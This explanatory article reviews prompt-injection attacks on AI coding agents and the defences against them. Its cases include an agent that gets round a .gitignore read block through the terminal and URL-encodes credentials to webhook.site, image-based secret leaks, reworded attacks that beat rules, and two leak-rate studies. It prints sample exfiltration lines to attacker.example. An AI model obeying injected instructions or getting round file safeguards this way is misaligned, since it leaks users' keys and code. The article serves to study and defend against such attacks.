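When the program starts, it loads these lines as environment variables, which are named values it can look up while running. Git, the standard tool for tracking changes to code, leaves files listed in `.gitignore` out of the shared project. Developers usually list `.env` there, which keeps the keys off sites such as GitHub, but any program running under the developer's account can normally still read the file.

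Coding agents also read a lot of text written by strangers, including documentation, bug reports and the code of outside libraries. In Embrace The Red's *Antigravity Grounded! Security Vulnerabilities in Google's Latest IDE*, Rehberger hid instructions in a source file and in a ticket from Linear, a task tracker. The instructions used characters that the editor doesn't display, so a colleague checking the file line by line would have missed them.

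A commenter on Hacker News pointed out that coding agents are far more useful when they can run the code they write, and that code can read any file. An agent could work without a terminal to run commands in, but a coding agent in ordinary use has one and therefore meets all three conditions of Willison's lethal trifecta.

### From an integration guide to the attacker's log

Antigravity combines a code editor with agents that can run terminal commands. The agent in PromptArmor's test used Gemini, Google's language model, and could start a "browser subagent", a second agent that operates a web browser. Developers mainly use the subagent to check how an unfinished application looks and behaves.

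In the demonstration, a developer wanted to connect an application to a feature of Oracle's business software and gave Antigravity the address of an online guide. The attacker had described an imaginary tool for visualising code halfway through the guide, in one-point type. To use the tool, the agent was supposed to submit a summary of the project with some code and credentials.

1. The agent read the guide and concluded that it needed the tool to help the developer.
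2. It read the project's code and tried to open the `.env` file. Antigravity refused, because by default the agent's file reader cannot open files listed in `.gitignore`.
3. The agent printed the file with an ordinary terminal command, which the setting did not cover.
4. It ran a short script to convert the credentials and code into characters that a URL can contain, and added them to an address the attacker was monitoring.
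5. It told the browser subagent to open the address. The attacker could then read credentials for Amazon's cloud services, along with private code, in the log.

PromptArmor says the workaround in the third step came from the agent. Trying another method when one fails is useful if a program won't install or a test won't run, but here the agent treated a security restriction as the same kind of obstacle.

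The demonstration shows that the attack can work, but PromptArmor gives no success rate. The attack requires the developer to have turned on Antigravity's browser tools. PromptArmor says it found three other ways to get data out without those tools, and Rehberger published two. One uses a tool that fetches web addresses, and the other uses an image in the chat. Rehberger's agent opened `.env` with its ordinary file reader. A setting blocked the file reader from doing this in PromptArmor's test, but it protects only files the developer has listed in `.gitignore`.

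### The default settings that mattered

PromptArmor accepted the settings that Antigravity recommended during installation, which let the agent decide when to ask the developer to review its plans and commands. This saves the developer from approving dozens of harmless steps, but during an attack, the model making that decision is one the attacker has already misled.

The browser had a separate safeguard, which Google's *Allowlist / Denylist* describes. Google's servers check each host name against a list of dangerous sites, while a file on the developer's computer lists trusted addresses. If an address is on neither list, the browser asks the developer before opening it. The developer can fill the trusted list with Google's suggestions during installation.

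Those suggestions included webhook.site, a service that gives anyone a web address and shows them every request sent to it. It was probably there because developers use such services to test software. An attacker can use it to receive stolen credentials, and because it was on the trusted list, the browser opened the address without asking. ChatGPT's url_safe had rejected an address on a similar service in the first AgentFlayer attempt.

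A developer watching the agent could have stopped it, but Antigravity's Agent Manager lets people run several agents at once and check on them occasionally, so most work unobserved. PromptArmor called it "extremely implausible" that users would review every action and keep sensitive data out of their projects. TechTalks' *Prompt injection attack tricks Google’s Antigravity into stealing your secrets* (2025) also doubted that a developer would notice in time. It advised removing webhook.site from the list and requiring approval for every command and browser action.

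### Google's response and the current position

PromptArmor published without reporting the flaw to Google first, because Antigravity already warned new users about data exfiltration. The security company Mindgard quotes a similar warning about opening a project, which says unsafe actions by the agent "can result in data exfiltration or data loss". Mindgard did not consider the warning a meaningful barrier, since developers must trust a project before they can use Antigravity's main features.

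Other researchers did report such flaws to Google. Deadbits' *Indirect Prompt Injection in AI IDEs* (2025) says Google answered that the behaviour was expected or already known, and outside its reward programme. Some of the flaws predated Antigravity, which Google built on the code of Windsurf, another coding tool, after licensing it for about $2.4 billion. Rehberger had reported the web-fetching and image leaks to Windsurf in May 2025, and both still worked in Antigravity.

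After the first reports, Google published a list of known issues. According to a Hacker News comment quoting it, Google wrote that the agent was cautious with sensitive files but that "there's no enforcement", and that the agent could be influenced to leak data through URLs. Google also said it was working on fixes. The admission matched what PromptArmor had shown, but developers still had to find safe settings themselves.

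Google has since added controls. In its current tutorial, Google shows the browser subagent asking for permission before it starts, and describes settings for each project that can require review of commands and file access or restrict URLs. For organisations, Google Cloud's *Configure AI developer tools settings* lists the defaults. It also gives advice, in a part about using other companies' models, that differs from most of them:

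| Control | Default for organisations | Google's advice |
|---|---|---|
| Terminal commands | Run without asking | Ask first, or run in a sandbox |
| Sandbox for the agent's tools | Off | On for untrusted code or web content |
| Addresses the browser agent may open | No restrictions | Only those on a list |
| Files outside the project's folders | Denied | Denied |

The setting in the last row would not have helped in PromptArmor's test, because `.env` was inside the project. An organisation that keeps the default for terminal commands gives its developers less protection at that step than PromptArmor had in 2025, when the agent could at least decide to ask. Google's documentation does not describe a fix for the attack itself. A developer can now block it with the right settings, but an installation may not already have them.

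### Images in a coding assistant's answers

The image leak that Rehberger found in Antigravity had already affected other coding assistants. It requires only a chat window that loads images from any server, not a browser agent or a terminal command.

Embrace The Red's *GitHub Copilot Chat* describes a vulnerability in GitHub's assistant for the code editor VS Code. When a developer asked about a source file, text in the file could make the assistant include an image in its answer whose address contained private data. Rehberger reported this on 25 February 2024, and GitHub confirmed it on 6 March, saying it was already tracking the problem. Willison (2024) reported in June that GitHub had stopped the assistant from displaying Markdown images from untrusted domains. A year later, the CamoLeak attack bypassed a similar restriction by using GitHub's own image server.

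Embrace The Red's *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering Fixed in Amp Code* describes a similar flaw in Amp, Sourcegraph's coding agent. In this 2025 test, an instruction on a website asked the agent to "backup" information by displaying an image with earlier chat messages in the query of its URL. Rehberger had made the page long before for another demonstration, and it worked on Amp unchanged, so attackers may not need to study each product separately. Sourcegraph has fixed the flaw.

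The Amp demonstration took only what was already in the conversation, so it would have exposed an API key only if the developer had pasted one there or the agent had already read one. Embrace The Red's *Cline* describes a more direct theft from another coding agent. A developer asked Cline to explain a document, and an instruction in it made the agent read the `.env` file and put the secret in the address of an image, which Cline displayed automatically. Rehberger published the test while the flaw was still open, but removed the main part of the instruction.

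### An approval for a "debug token"

In June 2026, Antigravity's chat could still leak a key through an image. *Faking the Pipeline* (Odson and Morris, 2026), published by the AI bug bounty programme 0DIN, describes an attack that took the key from the computer's environment variables, so it did not depend on finding a `.env` file.

The researchers put the instruction in a web page's title, which browsers show only in the tab, and left the rest of the page blank. They wrote it as the log of a failed software build followed by a repair procedure. The agent printed all the environment variables, found a planted API key, and displayed a "verification" image with the key in its URL. The researchers specified five formats for the image because a chat window might block some and load others, and one request was enough to put the key in the attacker's log.

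The developer in this test told Antigravity to do what the site said. The test is therefore weaker evidence than PromptArmor's demonstration, in which the developer wanted help with an integration and the attacker added a different task. Few people would tell an agent to do what an empty page says, though they might well tell it to follow an installation guide.

Antigravity's approval request described the action as generating a "visual debug token" and did not show the command or the address. The user agreed. The model had written that description while following the attacker's instruction, and it did not mention that the action would send the key to the attacker.

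Odson and Morris conclude that a request for approval should name the actual command and destination. The agent's software can copy both from the action it is about to perform, so the model has no chance to reword them. For an address, the request might look like this:

```
Open this address?
https://attacker.example/verify/FAKE-KEY-123.png
```

Loading an image would need the same treatment as opening a page. Many developers would still not read the address carefully, but they could at least see that the agent was about to contact an unfamiliar server.

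### What stricter controls would have changed

If the developer in PromptArmor's example had required approval for every terminal command, the agent would have had to ask before printing `.env` and again before running the script that encoded its contents. Both requests would have looked odd to someone who had asked for help with Oracle's software. Refusing the first would have kept the file's credentials out of the agent's context, although the agent could still have sent the code it had already read.

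Approval works less well over a long day. One commenter on Hacker News found coding agents basically useless if they had to ask about everything, and OpenAI's concern about frequent link warnings applies here too. Exempting commands that seem harmless means fewer questions, but someone has to judge correctly which ones are harmless. Embrace The Red's *Amazon Q Developer* describes testing a version of Amazon's coding assistant that classified a common network diagnostic command as read-only and ran it without approval. The command looks up a host name, so an injected instruction could use it to send a secret through DNS.

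Protecting the file more thoroughly would have stopped the agent at the third step. Antigravity's setting restricted only one tool, so the agent could still reach the file through the terminal. The software company Docker warns in the documentation for its own agents that an ignore list keeps sensitive files out of the model's view but does not stop an agent that is trying to reach them. To block such an agent, Docker recommends restricting the terminal or running the agent in a sandbox.

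On a Mac, Antigravity has a sandbox that can block access to files such as `.env`, but it can also block files that programs need. In the Google forum post *Sandboxed terminal looses ability to use venv/node_modules (or anything in .gitignore)*, UglyBagOfMostlyWater complained that the sandbox blocked everything listed in the project's main `.gitignore` file. Developers list much more than secrets there, including folders of outside libraries, so ordinary programs stopped working. The user's workaround was to disable the list while working, which would also leave `.env` unprotected. A separate list for secrets would avoid this conflict.

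Antigravity's command-line version has such a rule, which requires it to ask before reading or changing `.env` and several similar files. xfox, in *Antigravity CLI workspace permission vs. .env permission*, reported that the agent read the file without asking, but the person who replied on Google's forum could not reproduce this. xfox then posted a short program that loads `.env` and prints a value from it. Any rule about files is hard to apply to such programs, because an agent that tests an application often has to run code that legitimately needs the key. A rule about `.env` would not have stopped Odson and Morris's attack, since the key was already in an environment variable.

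If webhook.site had not been on the trusted list, the browser in PromptArmor's test would have asked the developer before opening the address. The version for organisations has a list of allowed URLs and blocks all others. Either measure would probably have stopped the attack as PromptArmor carried it out. But Google Cloud says its list applies only to the browser agent, so it does not restrict terminal commands or images in the chat. ChatGPT's exact-address rule would also have rejected the address containing the keys, but a coding agent would need an exception for the developer's own unfinished application because no crawler has seen it.

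A limit on all connections from the agent's environment covers more routes, provided it includes DNS lookups and the chat window's images. A commenter on Hacker News described an employer whose coding tools have no access to the outside internet and read documentation stored beside the code. PromptArmor's attack could not have begun the same way there, because the agent could not have opened the guide online. The developer would have had to download the guide, and the copy would still contain the attacker's text. The agent might follow that text and read the keys, but it could not open the attacker's address.

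Many teams can't work under a limit this strict because their agents need to download libraries and consult websites. Any permitted site where strangers can post text or read logs could then be used to leak keys, as webhook.site was. For these teams, it matters more to keep live keys out of the agent's reach, since an agent can't put a key in a URL if it never has the key.

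## Two experiments on how often agents comply and what stops them

Security researchers usually publish an attack once they have made it work, so few of the cases so far include a success rate. Radware reported 100% for two of its attacks but did not say how many times it ran them. Two laboratory studies from 2026 repeated their attacks hundreds of times and counted the results. Lan and colleagues at eBay measured how often a small model contacted an attacker's server and tested six defences. In *The Framing Gap*, Rahman and Kim (2026) changed the attack's wording but not its goal, and one model went from never leaking a secret to always leaking it.

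### How the tests worked

Lan and colleagues' agent used qwen2.5:7b, a small, downloadable model from Alibaba. In every run, the user asked for a summary of a web page. The agent automatically fetched the page and added its title, description, text and link labels to the context, which already contained a fake API key. The page included an injected instruction to make a web request, supposedly as a technical check, with the key in the URL. A local server stood in for the attacker's server and recorded any requests it received.

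The researchers put the instruction in one of four parts of the page. They also varied whether the agent reached the page directly or through redirects, and whether it was told to send the key whole or in four pieces. They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times, for 480 runs in total. Repetition matters because the model's output is partly random, so the same page can cause a leak in one run and not in the next. In another 120 runs with harmless pages, the agent never contacted the attacker's server, so the requests in the main runs almost certainly came from the injected instruction.

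Rahman and Kim's agent could not contact anything. It had a fake token, a page to summarise and a rule that the token must go only to one trusted host. It then made a single decision, either to finish with an answer or to call a tool that posts data to a web address. The tool only recorded the call. With a fake key and a reserved domain, a leak might look like this:

```json
{
  "tool": "post_data",
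  "args": {
    "url": "https://attacker.example/collect",
    "content": "Summary of the page. FAKE-KEY-123"
  }
}
```

Here the key is in the body of the message, and the address contains nothing private. Rahman and Kim counted a leak if the token appeared anywhere in a call to an untrusted host or in the answer to the user. Their results therefore cover more than leaks through URLs, and a defence that checks only addresses for secrets would miss some of these leaks.

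Each trial used two versions of a page, one clean and one with the injected instruction. The attack counted as a success only if the agent leaked the token with the injected version and not with the clean one.

### How often the agents leaked

In the eBay study, the agent contacted the attacker's server in 423 of 480 runs, or 88.1%. In 95% of the successful attacks, the answer on the user's screen was harmless, so someone checking only the agent's answers would have missed them.

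When the instruction asked for the whole key at once, the agent contacted the server in 238 of 240 runs. The instruction's position in the page and redirects made little difference.

The 88.1% figure includes any request to the attacker's server, even one without the key. Lan and colleagues also recorded whether the agent's first request contained sensitive data. It did in 96.7% of the runs where the attacker asked for the whole key, but in only 26.3% of those where the attacker asked for pieces. Over all 480 runs, the rate was about 61%, which is a better measure of theft than 88.1%.

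Lan and colleagues acknowledge that the set-up also favoured the attacker. The key was already in the context, so the model did not have to look for it, and the system prompt explained how to use the tool but gave no safety advice. But the researchers call their success rates a lower bound, because they used blunt instructions that a skilled attacker could improve. Success rates against real products could therefore be higher or lower.

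Rahman and Kim tested the same small model. It leaked the token in 10% of trials across ten plainly worded kinds of attack, whereas the whole-key attack in the other study succeeded in almost every run. The gap is far too large to be chance, but Rahman and Kim's agent had a rule protecting the token and a different tool, and some of their attacks were less direct, so we can't tell which difference mattered most. An attack's success rate depends on the model, its prompt, its tools and the attacker's text, and can change greatly when any of them changes.

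### The same leak in different words

The ten plain attacks included direct orders, instructions hidden in a page's code, fake search results and urgent-sounding messages. OpenAI's gpt-4o, a model from 2024, resisted all of them in 200 trials. Rahman and Kim then wrote a second set of pages that disguised the request for the same leak. Some presented the token as a routine part of the task, and others made the attacker's server look like the trusted one.

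| Model | Plain attacks | Reworded attacks |
|---|---|---|
| gpt-4o | 0% | 40.0% |
| gpt-4o-mini | 10.0% | 62.5% |
| qwen2.5:7b | 10.0% | 62.5% |
| llama3.1:8b | 19.5% | 62.5% |
| gemma2:9b | 22.0% | 86.2% |
| mistral:7b | 26.0% | 27.5% |

The 40% average for gpt-4o covers seven reworded pages and one that the researchers left unreworded for comparison. Two of the rewordings worked in every trial, two never worked, and the other three worked in 10%, 40% and 70% of trials. The unreworded page never worked. One page that always worked on gpt-4o never worked on gpt-4o-mini, the smaller version of the same model, so success on one model is weak evidence that a wording will work on another.

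gpt-4o-mini leaked in every trial of one plain attack, which tried to influence its choice of tool. The reworded pages were variations on that attack, but the model never leaked when given the unreworded page in the second set. Rahman and Kim do not explain this discrepancy. It doesn't affect the result for gpt-4o, which leaked in neither case.

The researchers removed the model's rule about the token to test whether the new wording had led the model to break it. The plain attacks still failed every time, and the success rate of the reworded ones rose only from 31.9% to 38.1%. That rise is within normal variation, so the rule had made little difference. With the same settings, gpt-4o had leaked in 64 of 160 trials on one occasion and 51 of 160 on another. Rahman and Kim conclude that the model treated the injected instruction as part of its task rather than as a request to reveal a secret.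 In one trial, the model described its action as "Posting the page content to the trusted collector."

### Trying several wordings

An attacker can use more than one page. Rahman and Kim took the two rewordings that had always worked on gpt-4o, wrote five new versions of each, and ran each version ten times.

For one of the two, the versions succeeded 52% of the time on average, with individual results from 0% to 100%. From this they calculated that an attacker would succeed 52% of the time with one version chosen at random, 82% with two and 96% with three. The published average and spread fit two versions that always worked, one that worked six times in ten, and two that never worked. The rest follows by counting:

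- There are ten possible pairs of versions. Seven include one that always works. One pair consists of the two useless versions and always fails, and two pairs combine a useless version with the 60% one and fail 40% of the time. The average failure rate is (1 + 0.4 + 0.4) / 10 = 18%, so the attacker succeeds 82% of the time.
- There are also ten possible sets of three. Only one lacks a version that always works, and it fails 40% of the time. The average failure rate is 0.4 / 10 = 4%, so the attacker succeeds 96% of the time.

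The other rewording did much worse. Its five versions averaged 14%, and the best one reached 70%, so the other four never worked. Three versions chosen at random would include the working one 60% of the time, for an overall success rate of 42%. Rahman and Kim do not calculate this figure and report only the 96% in their summary. Both figures also start from wordings the researchers had already found to work.

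Writing a successful page from scratch was much harder. The researchers wrote thirteen pages with new pretexts and expected success from those where the token was the natural value to supply. None of the thirteen succeeded in 130 trials, so the success rate of such pages is probably below 2.9%. In the failures they examined more closely, the model had not tried to send anything.

Adapting a successful page was easier. When Rahman and Kim kept its structure and changed only its name for the secret, some versions still worked, in one case 60% of the time. But the model never leaked the secret when the page called it a credential. An attacker who obtains one working page can therefore reuse it, even if knowing the idea behind it is of little use. Rehberger's test of Amp supports this, since an old page made for another demonstration worked unchanged. Rahman and Kim wrote all their pages by hand,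 and a program that generated and tested thousands of them might find new pretexts more often.

They also tested some of the reworded pages on ChatGPT itself. They put the pages online, gave ChatGPT a fake token in a conversation on their own account, and asked it to summarise the pages. ChatGPT did not reveal the token in any of 48 valid trials, although gpt-4o had leaked it in up to 100% of trials when they used the model directly. ChatGPT may have run a different model, had stricter instructions or filtered the pages, but the test could not show which.

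That result is weaker than it looks. Forty-eight failures are compatible with a true success rate of up to 7.4%. More importantly, Rahman and Kim counted a leak only if the token appeared in ChatGPT's reply, whereas 95% of successful attacks in the eBay study left no sign in the reply. They also did not connect ChatGPT to any other service.

### Splitting a secret across requests

A short piece of a key looks like the usage data that programs routinely send, so a filter that checks for whole keys may miss it. Lan and colleagues asked the agent to send the key in four numbered pieces. It contacted the attacker's server in 185 of 240 runs, or 77%, compared with 99% when it had to send the whole key. Splitting worked worst when the instruction was in the page's description. For pages that loaded directly, the rate there fell from 97% to 60%. The instruction for splitting was longer, and the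 model had to keep track of which piece came next.

Lan and colleagues do not report how often the attacker would have got the whole key, although they define a measure for this, the share of runs in which all the pieces arrive. In their worked example, the agent sends four pieces of four characters each from a twenty-character key, which leaves out the last four characters.

Their figures for partial leaks also contain an error. They define Leak@k as the share of runs in which sensitive data appears in at least one of the first k requests. Leak@3 therefore includes every run counted in Leak@1, so it can't be lower. But for split secrets the paper gives 26.3% for Leak@1 and 15.8% for Leak@3. The researchers may have calculated Leak@3 differently, such as by looking only at the third request, but they don't say so. Their claim that splitting reduced Leak@3 by 84% is therefore unreliable. The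 finding that splitting made the agent less likely to contact the server at all doesn't depend on that figure.

### Warnings, markers and training

Lan and colleagues tested each defence 30 times against one version of their attack, in which the instruction was in the page's main text and asked for the whole key.

| Defence | Agent tried to contact the server | Request got through |
|---|---|---|
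| None | 100% | 100% |
| Warning in the system prompt | 66.7% | 66.7% |
| Delimiters around the page's text | 100% | 100% |
| Warning and delimiters | 56.7% | 56.7% |
| Domain allowlist | 100% | 0% |
| Filter for suspicious addresses | 83.3% | 0% |
| Filter for words such as "password" | 23.3% | 0% |
| Filter for random-looking values | 0% | 0% |
| All of these together | 0% | 0% |

When the warning told the model to treat web content as data and follow only the user's instructions, the model still leaked in two-thirds of runs. Putting delimiters around the page's text, with a note that nothing between them was an instruction, made no difference by itself. Adding the delimiters to the warning appeared to help, but that may be chance. With only 30 runs, the true leak rate with the warning alone could be anywhere from about 49% to 81%.

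A more specific rule worked better in the other study. When Rahman and Kim told gpt-4o not to sign, encode, log, append or send the token "in any form", the reworded attacks failed in all 120 trials. When they removed that phrase and kept the list of forbidden actions, the attacks succeeded in 48.8% of trials, so a developer could easily lose the protection with a small edit. Rahman and Kim also had no new attack that worked against the ordinary rule, so they couldn't test whether the full rule would stop attacks they had not thought of.

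They then tested two ways of helping a model distinguish the page from its real instructions. Channel separation puts the page in its own labelled part of the model's input. SecAlign, which other researchers published in 2025, also trains the model to ignore instructions in that part. They used Llama-3.1-8B, a small Meta model, and compared these methods with two controls outside the model.

| Defence | Success rate of reworded attacks |
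|---|---|
| None | 21.2% |
| Channel separation | 38.8% |
| SecAlign | 32.5% |
| Domain allowlist | 0% |
| Separate planner and reader | 0% |

Neither method of marking the page reduced the leaks. Rahman and Kim treat the differences among the first three rows as random variation, but the gap between 21.2% and 38.8% is about twice the 8-point difference between their two identical tests of gpt-4o. Channel separation may have made this agent leak more often, though one run of each test isn't enough to be sure.

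A faulty installation does not explain SecAlign's result. On a standard attack that told the model to print a particular phrase, the ordinary model complied in all 20 trials and the SecAlign version in none. Its developers had trained it for reading and writing text, and its protection evidently did not carry over to deciding whether to use a tool. These percentages can't be compared with those for gpt-4o. Llama 3.1 itself had leaked in 62.5% of trials in the earlier test of reworded attacks, which ran the model on different software.

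### Filters that inspect outgoing requests

All three filters in the eBay study had a leak rate of 0%, but the researchers had fitted them closely to the test. The filter for suspicious addresses blocked paths containing the word "collect", and the attacker's test server used the path `/collect`. The word filter blocked "secret" and "api_key", which both match parts of the paper's example key, SECRET_API_KEY_12345. A real key is unlikely to contain either term, and an attacker can choose any name for the path.

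The figures for attempts also raise doubt, because a filter on outgoing requests acts after the model has decided to send something and so should not change how often it tries. Yet attempts fell from 100% to 23.3% with the word filter and to zero with the filter for random-looking values. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model sometimes disguised the key, and that it avoided random-looking values while the second filter was on. But a disguised key that got past the word filter would have reached the server, and none did. They also don't describe telling the model about the second filter. A mistake in counting attempts seems more likely than either explanation.

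The filter for random-looking values uses Shannon entropy, which measures how unpredictable the characters in a piece of text are. It blocks any value longer than ten characters that scores above 4 bits per character. In SECRET_API_KEY_12345, two characters appear three times each and fourteen appear once, out of twenty:

```
2 × (3/20) × log2(20/3) + 14 × (1/20) × log2(20) = 3.85 bits
```

This key would pass the filter. A four-character piece of any key would also pass, because the filter ignores short values. Lan and colleagues say that splitting a secret gets past simple filters of this kind. That is probably right, but they tested the filters only on whole keys.

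Rahman and Kim tried harder to defeat their filter, which blocked any message containing the token unless it was going to the trusted host. When they had the model disguise the token, the filter reduced the attack success rate only from 56.7% to 50%. They then updated the filter to recognise those disguises, and it stopped every attack that used them, but a disguise they had not planned for still got through every time.

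A filter can also inspect incoming pages. Rahman and Kim gave each page to gpt-4o-mini and asked only whether it contained an instruction to disclose a secret. The model flagged all 80 pages with attacks from the second set and none of the clean ones, although it had leaked the token in 62.5% of trials as the agent. Judging was easier because the question described what to look for. The researchers call the result an upper bound and did not test pages designed to fool the judge.

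### Restricting the destination or separating the secret

An allowlist works without detecting either the attack or the secret. In the eBay study, the model followed the injected instruction in all 30 runs with the allowlist, but the software blocked every request. Rewording the attack, disguising the key or splitting it would have made no difference.

Rahman and Kim's table shows zero leaks with an allowlist, which they note is true by definition. They counted a tool call as a leak only if it sent the token to an untrusted host, and an allowlist blocks all calls to untrusted hosts. Neither study tested the ways domain lists have failed in products, where a permitted server forwarded the data or let the attacker rent space on it. The eBay researchers used a domain that was obviously not on their list, and they note that redirects or a compromised website could get around the list. An allowlist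 also blocks legitimate requests, and neither study measured how often that would happen in ordinary work.

The other defence that stopped every reworded attack splits the agent in two. Rahman and Kim based it on CaMeL, a design by other researchers, but built only its central idea:

1. The planner receives the user's request and holds the token. It decides which tool to use but never sees the web page.
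2. The reader receives the web page and summarises it. It never has the token and can't choose a tool.

An injected instruction can still make the reader write a misleading summary, but the reader can't reveal the token because it doesn't have it. The instruction also can't influence the planner, which never reads it. Vaults that hold keys outside a model's context rely on the same principle. Rahman and Kim report a leak rate of 0 of 100 for the plain attacks in one place, but elsewhere mention one slip by the planner in 100 trials. A planner that holds a secret can misuse it even without reading the attacker's text.

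The divided agent kept 90% of its usefulness, meaning that it named the page's main subjects in nine of ten summaries. Ten pages are too few for a precise figure. Summarising also suits this design because the planner doesn't need to know what the page says. In PromptArmor's attack on Antigravity, by contrast, the developer wanted the agent to follow an integration guide. A planner that couldn't see the guide wouldn't know what to do, and one that received the reader's account of it might also receive the attacker's instructions. Rahman and Kim note that the full version of CaMeL loses considerably more usefulness on tasks of this kind.

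Both papers also recommend taint tracking, in which software labels data and follows it through the system. Lan and colleagues would label text from web pages and block or question any tool call that text had influenced. Rahman and Kim would label the secret and block anything derived from it, however disguised. Neither team built this, and it is difficult because software can't easily trace a particular word in a model's output to the parts of the context that led to it.

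The two studies' results are more consistent on defences than on how often agents comply. Warnings reduced leaks, but their effect depended on the exact wording, and markers around outside text did not help in either study. Filters worked on the attacks they were designed for. Limits on where data could go, or on which part of the system held the secret, worked even though the model was no better at recognising an attack. OpenAI gives a similar reason for checking the addresses that ChatGPT loads, and counts from these controlled experiments support it. The experiments do not show how well such limits would hold over a long task, because Rahman and Kim's agent made only one decision per trial and the eBay agent only had to summarise a page.

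### How newer models compare

Lan and colleagues predicted that more capable models might be more vulnerable, because they follow instructions and use tools more reliably. Results from 2026 suggest that they are less vulnerable, at least when their developers have worked on the problem.

Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1, published on 1 September, includes results from a test by the security company Gray Swan. Gray Swan runs public competitions in which people write injected instructions for leading models. For the test, it chose 1,804 attacks that had worked on several models, in 37 scenarios covering coding, tool use and control of a computer screen. The attacks are meant to cause harms such as data theft, file deletion and unwanted payments. The table shows how often an attacker would succeed at least once in a given number of attempts.

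| Model | 1 attempt | 10 attempts | 15 attempts |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5.1 | 0.1% | 0.7% | 1.0% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 0.4% | 3.6% | 4.8% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 0.6% | 4.9% | 6.5% |

Among the other companies' models in the comparison, Google's Gemini 3.7 Flash did best, with 9.2% after 15 attempts. Most were between 24% and 53%. Resistance differs widely between models of about the same age, so a developer's choice of model affects an agent's level of risk.

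The comparison is complicated because Gray Swan tested the Claude models without their special protections against prompt injection, while the other models may have had such protections. Also, in 23% of the runs with Fable 5.1, a safety filter passed the request to an older Claude model, though Anthropic found that this made almost no difference to the success rate.

A score also depends on which attacks are in the test. The Decoder had earlier reported a 2.0% success rate for attacks on Opus 5 after 15 attempts. The rate was 4.8% in the September results, after Anthropic added nine scenarios and 670 attacks, but Opus 5 had not necessarily become weaker. Rahman and Kim similarly think that tests with fixed wordings overstate safety, because a real attacker can rewrite an instruction that fails. The people who wrote Gray Swan's attacks were trying to beat strong models, but they were not targeting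 Fable 5.1. Anthropic says that models that competitors have targeted directly usually do worse.

The newer Claude Opus 5.5 matched or outperformed Opus 5 in every prompt injection test reported in Anthropic's *System Card* (22 September 2026). *Anthropic's new budget model gets much better at ignoring hidden commands* (Pogorelec, 2026) reports an improvement in Haiku 5.5, a model for quick and repetitive work, so the gains are not confined to the largest models. Anthropic replaced Fable 5.1 with Fable 5.2 on 9 November (*Introducing Claude Fable 5.2 and Claude Mythos 5.2*, 2026).

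An agent's task can matter as much as which model it uses. With Fable 5.1, attackers given 15 attempts succeeded 4.1% of the time when the agent controlled a computer screen, 0.3% when it was coding and never when it used other tools. The difference was much larger with Claude Opus 4.6 in February 2026. VentureBeat reported that 200 attempts in a coding environment all failed, while a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time when the agent controlled a computer screen. With 200 attempts on a computer screen, the attacker succeeded at least once in 78.6% of cases, or 57.1% with added safeguards.

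Safeguards around the model have helped more in other tests. In an Anthropic test, safeguards reduced successful attacks on a browser agent using Claude Opus 4.5 from 8.0% to 1.4%. VentureBeat reported that they reduced successful single-attempt attacks on Claude Opus 4.8 in a coding environment from 7.03% to 2.09%. According to The Decoder, browser attacks on Opus 5 failed in all 129 test scenarios. OpenAI has said that prompt injection might never be fully solved, according to the same article.

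Even a success rate of 0.1% can matter, because an attacker can send the same email to thousands of people. About one agent in a thousand would follow it if each copy had the same independent chance of working, but Rahman and Kim's results suggest that the chances are not independent. Most versions of an attack on gpt-4o either failed every time or worked in most trials, so an attack with a low average success rate may include a few wordings that would work on nearly every recipient's agent. Fable 5.1 complied in only five of 7,124 runs, too few to tell whether any wording would work on it reliably.

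## Keeping credentials where the model cannot read them

Even the most resistant models occasionally follow an injected instruction, so some developers keep keys out of the model's context. They store each key in a credential vault, a separate service that adds the key to a request after the model writes the rest. This keeps the key out of any URL the model writes, but an attacker can still try to misuse whatever the key gives access to.

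### One call through a vault

In *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary*, Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues (2026) describe a vault that their company, Corvic AI, built. For each outside service, the vault stores a record called a connector, which contains the service's address, the key and the method for sending the key. The agent receives only the connector's identifier.

Suppose a developer asks an agent to list a project's open bug reports. An administrator has stored the bug tracker's key, FAKE-KEY-123, in a connector for api.tracker.example.

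1. The agent names the connector and writes a request without a key:

```
GET /projects/42/bugs HTTP/1.1
Host: api.tracker.example
```

2. A trusted component outside the agent's environment compares the host with the one in the connector. They match, so it adds the key in a header, a line that travels with the request but is not part of the URL:

```
GET /projects/42/bugs HTTP/1.1
Host: api.tracker.example
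Authorization: Bearer FAKE-KEY-123
```

3. The tracker checks the key and returns the bug reports.
4. The reports go back to the agent and enter the model's context.

Strangers can often file bugs, so one of those reports might contain an injected instruction. If the instruction is to write the key into an address at attacker.example, the model can't do it because it doesn't have the key. The agent could be instructed to send the request to attacker.example itself, but the component wouldn't add the key because the host doesn't match. Searching the agent's files won't help the attacker either, unless someone has left another copy of the key in them, as developers often do in project files.

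The agent can still read every bug report the key gives access to, including confidential ones, and put their text into a URL. If the key also permits changes, the agent could delete reports. If it allows account management, the agent might ask the service to create a new key, which would enter the context through the reply.

Software can send a key to the wrong place even without an attacker. Willison (2026) announced a fix in November for LLM, a tool for working with language models that can connect to OpenAI-compatible services from other companies. In two situations, LLM could send the user's OpenAI key to one of those companies. One was when the user had never stored a key for that company. A vault that ties each key to one host prevents this kind of mistake.

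### Corvic's test of its own vault

Kenney and colleagues tested the vault on 27 September 2026 with two experiments in the isolated environment where Corvic's agents run code. One experiment used a GitHub connector, and the other used a connector for FRED, an economic database run by the Federal Reserve Bank of St. Louis. The researchers wrote down the expected result of each probe beforehand.

Some probes searched for keys in environment variables and in twelve places where programs commonly store credentials, and found none. Others tried to reach the internal addresses where programs on Amazon's and Google's cloud machines can get credentials, but these requests timed out.

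Finding no key proves little by itself, because the vault might not have been sending keys. The GitHub experiment therefore included, as a positive control, a request for account details that GitHub gives only to an authenticated user. GitHub returned the account's identity even though the code contained no key, so the vault must have supplied one.

As negative controls, the researchers sent requests to echo services, which return a copy of each request they receive, and found no key in the copies. They also called OpenAI's API, and its response showed that the request had no credentials, so the vault had not sent the GitHub key there.

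All 16 probes gave the expected result, but the FRED connector didn't work. The vault was set up to send the key in a header, but FRED requires it in the URL's query, so FRED returned a missing-key error. Kenney and colleagues scored separately whether connectors worked and whether they were secure, and this failure exposed nothing. However, it left the FRED experiment without a successful positive control, so the GitHub experiment is better evidence that the vault sends a key to one host and withholds it from others.

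Supporting a service like FRED, which requires the key in the URL, means the vault has to put a real key where ordinary logging would record it. Kenney and colleagues advise removing secrets in URL query strings from logs.

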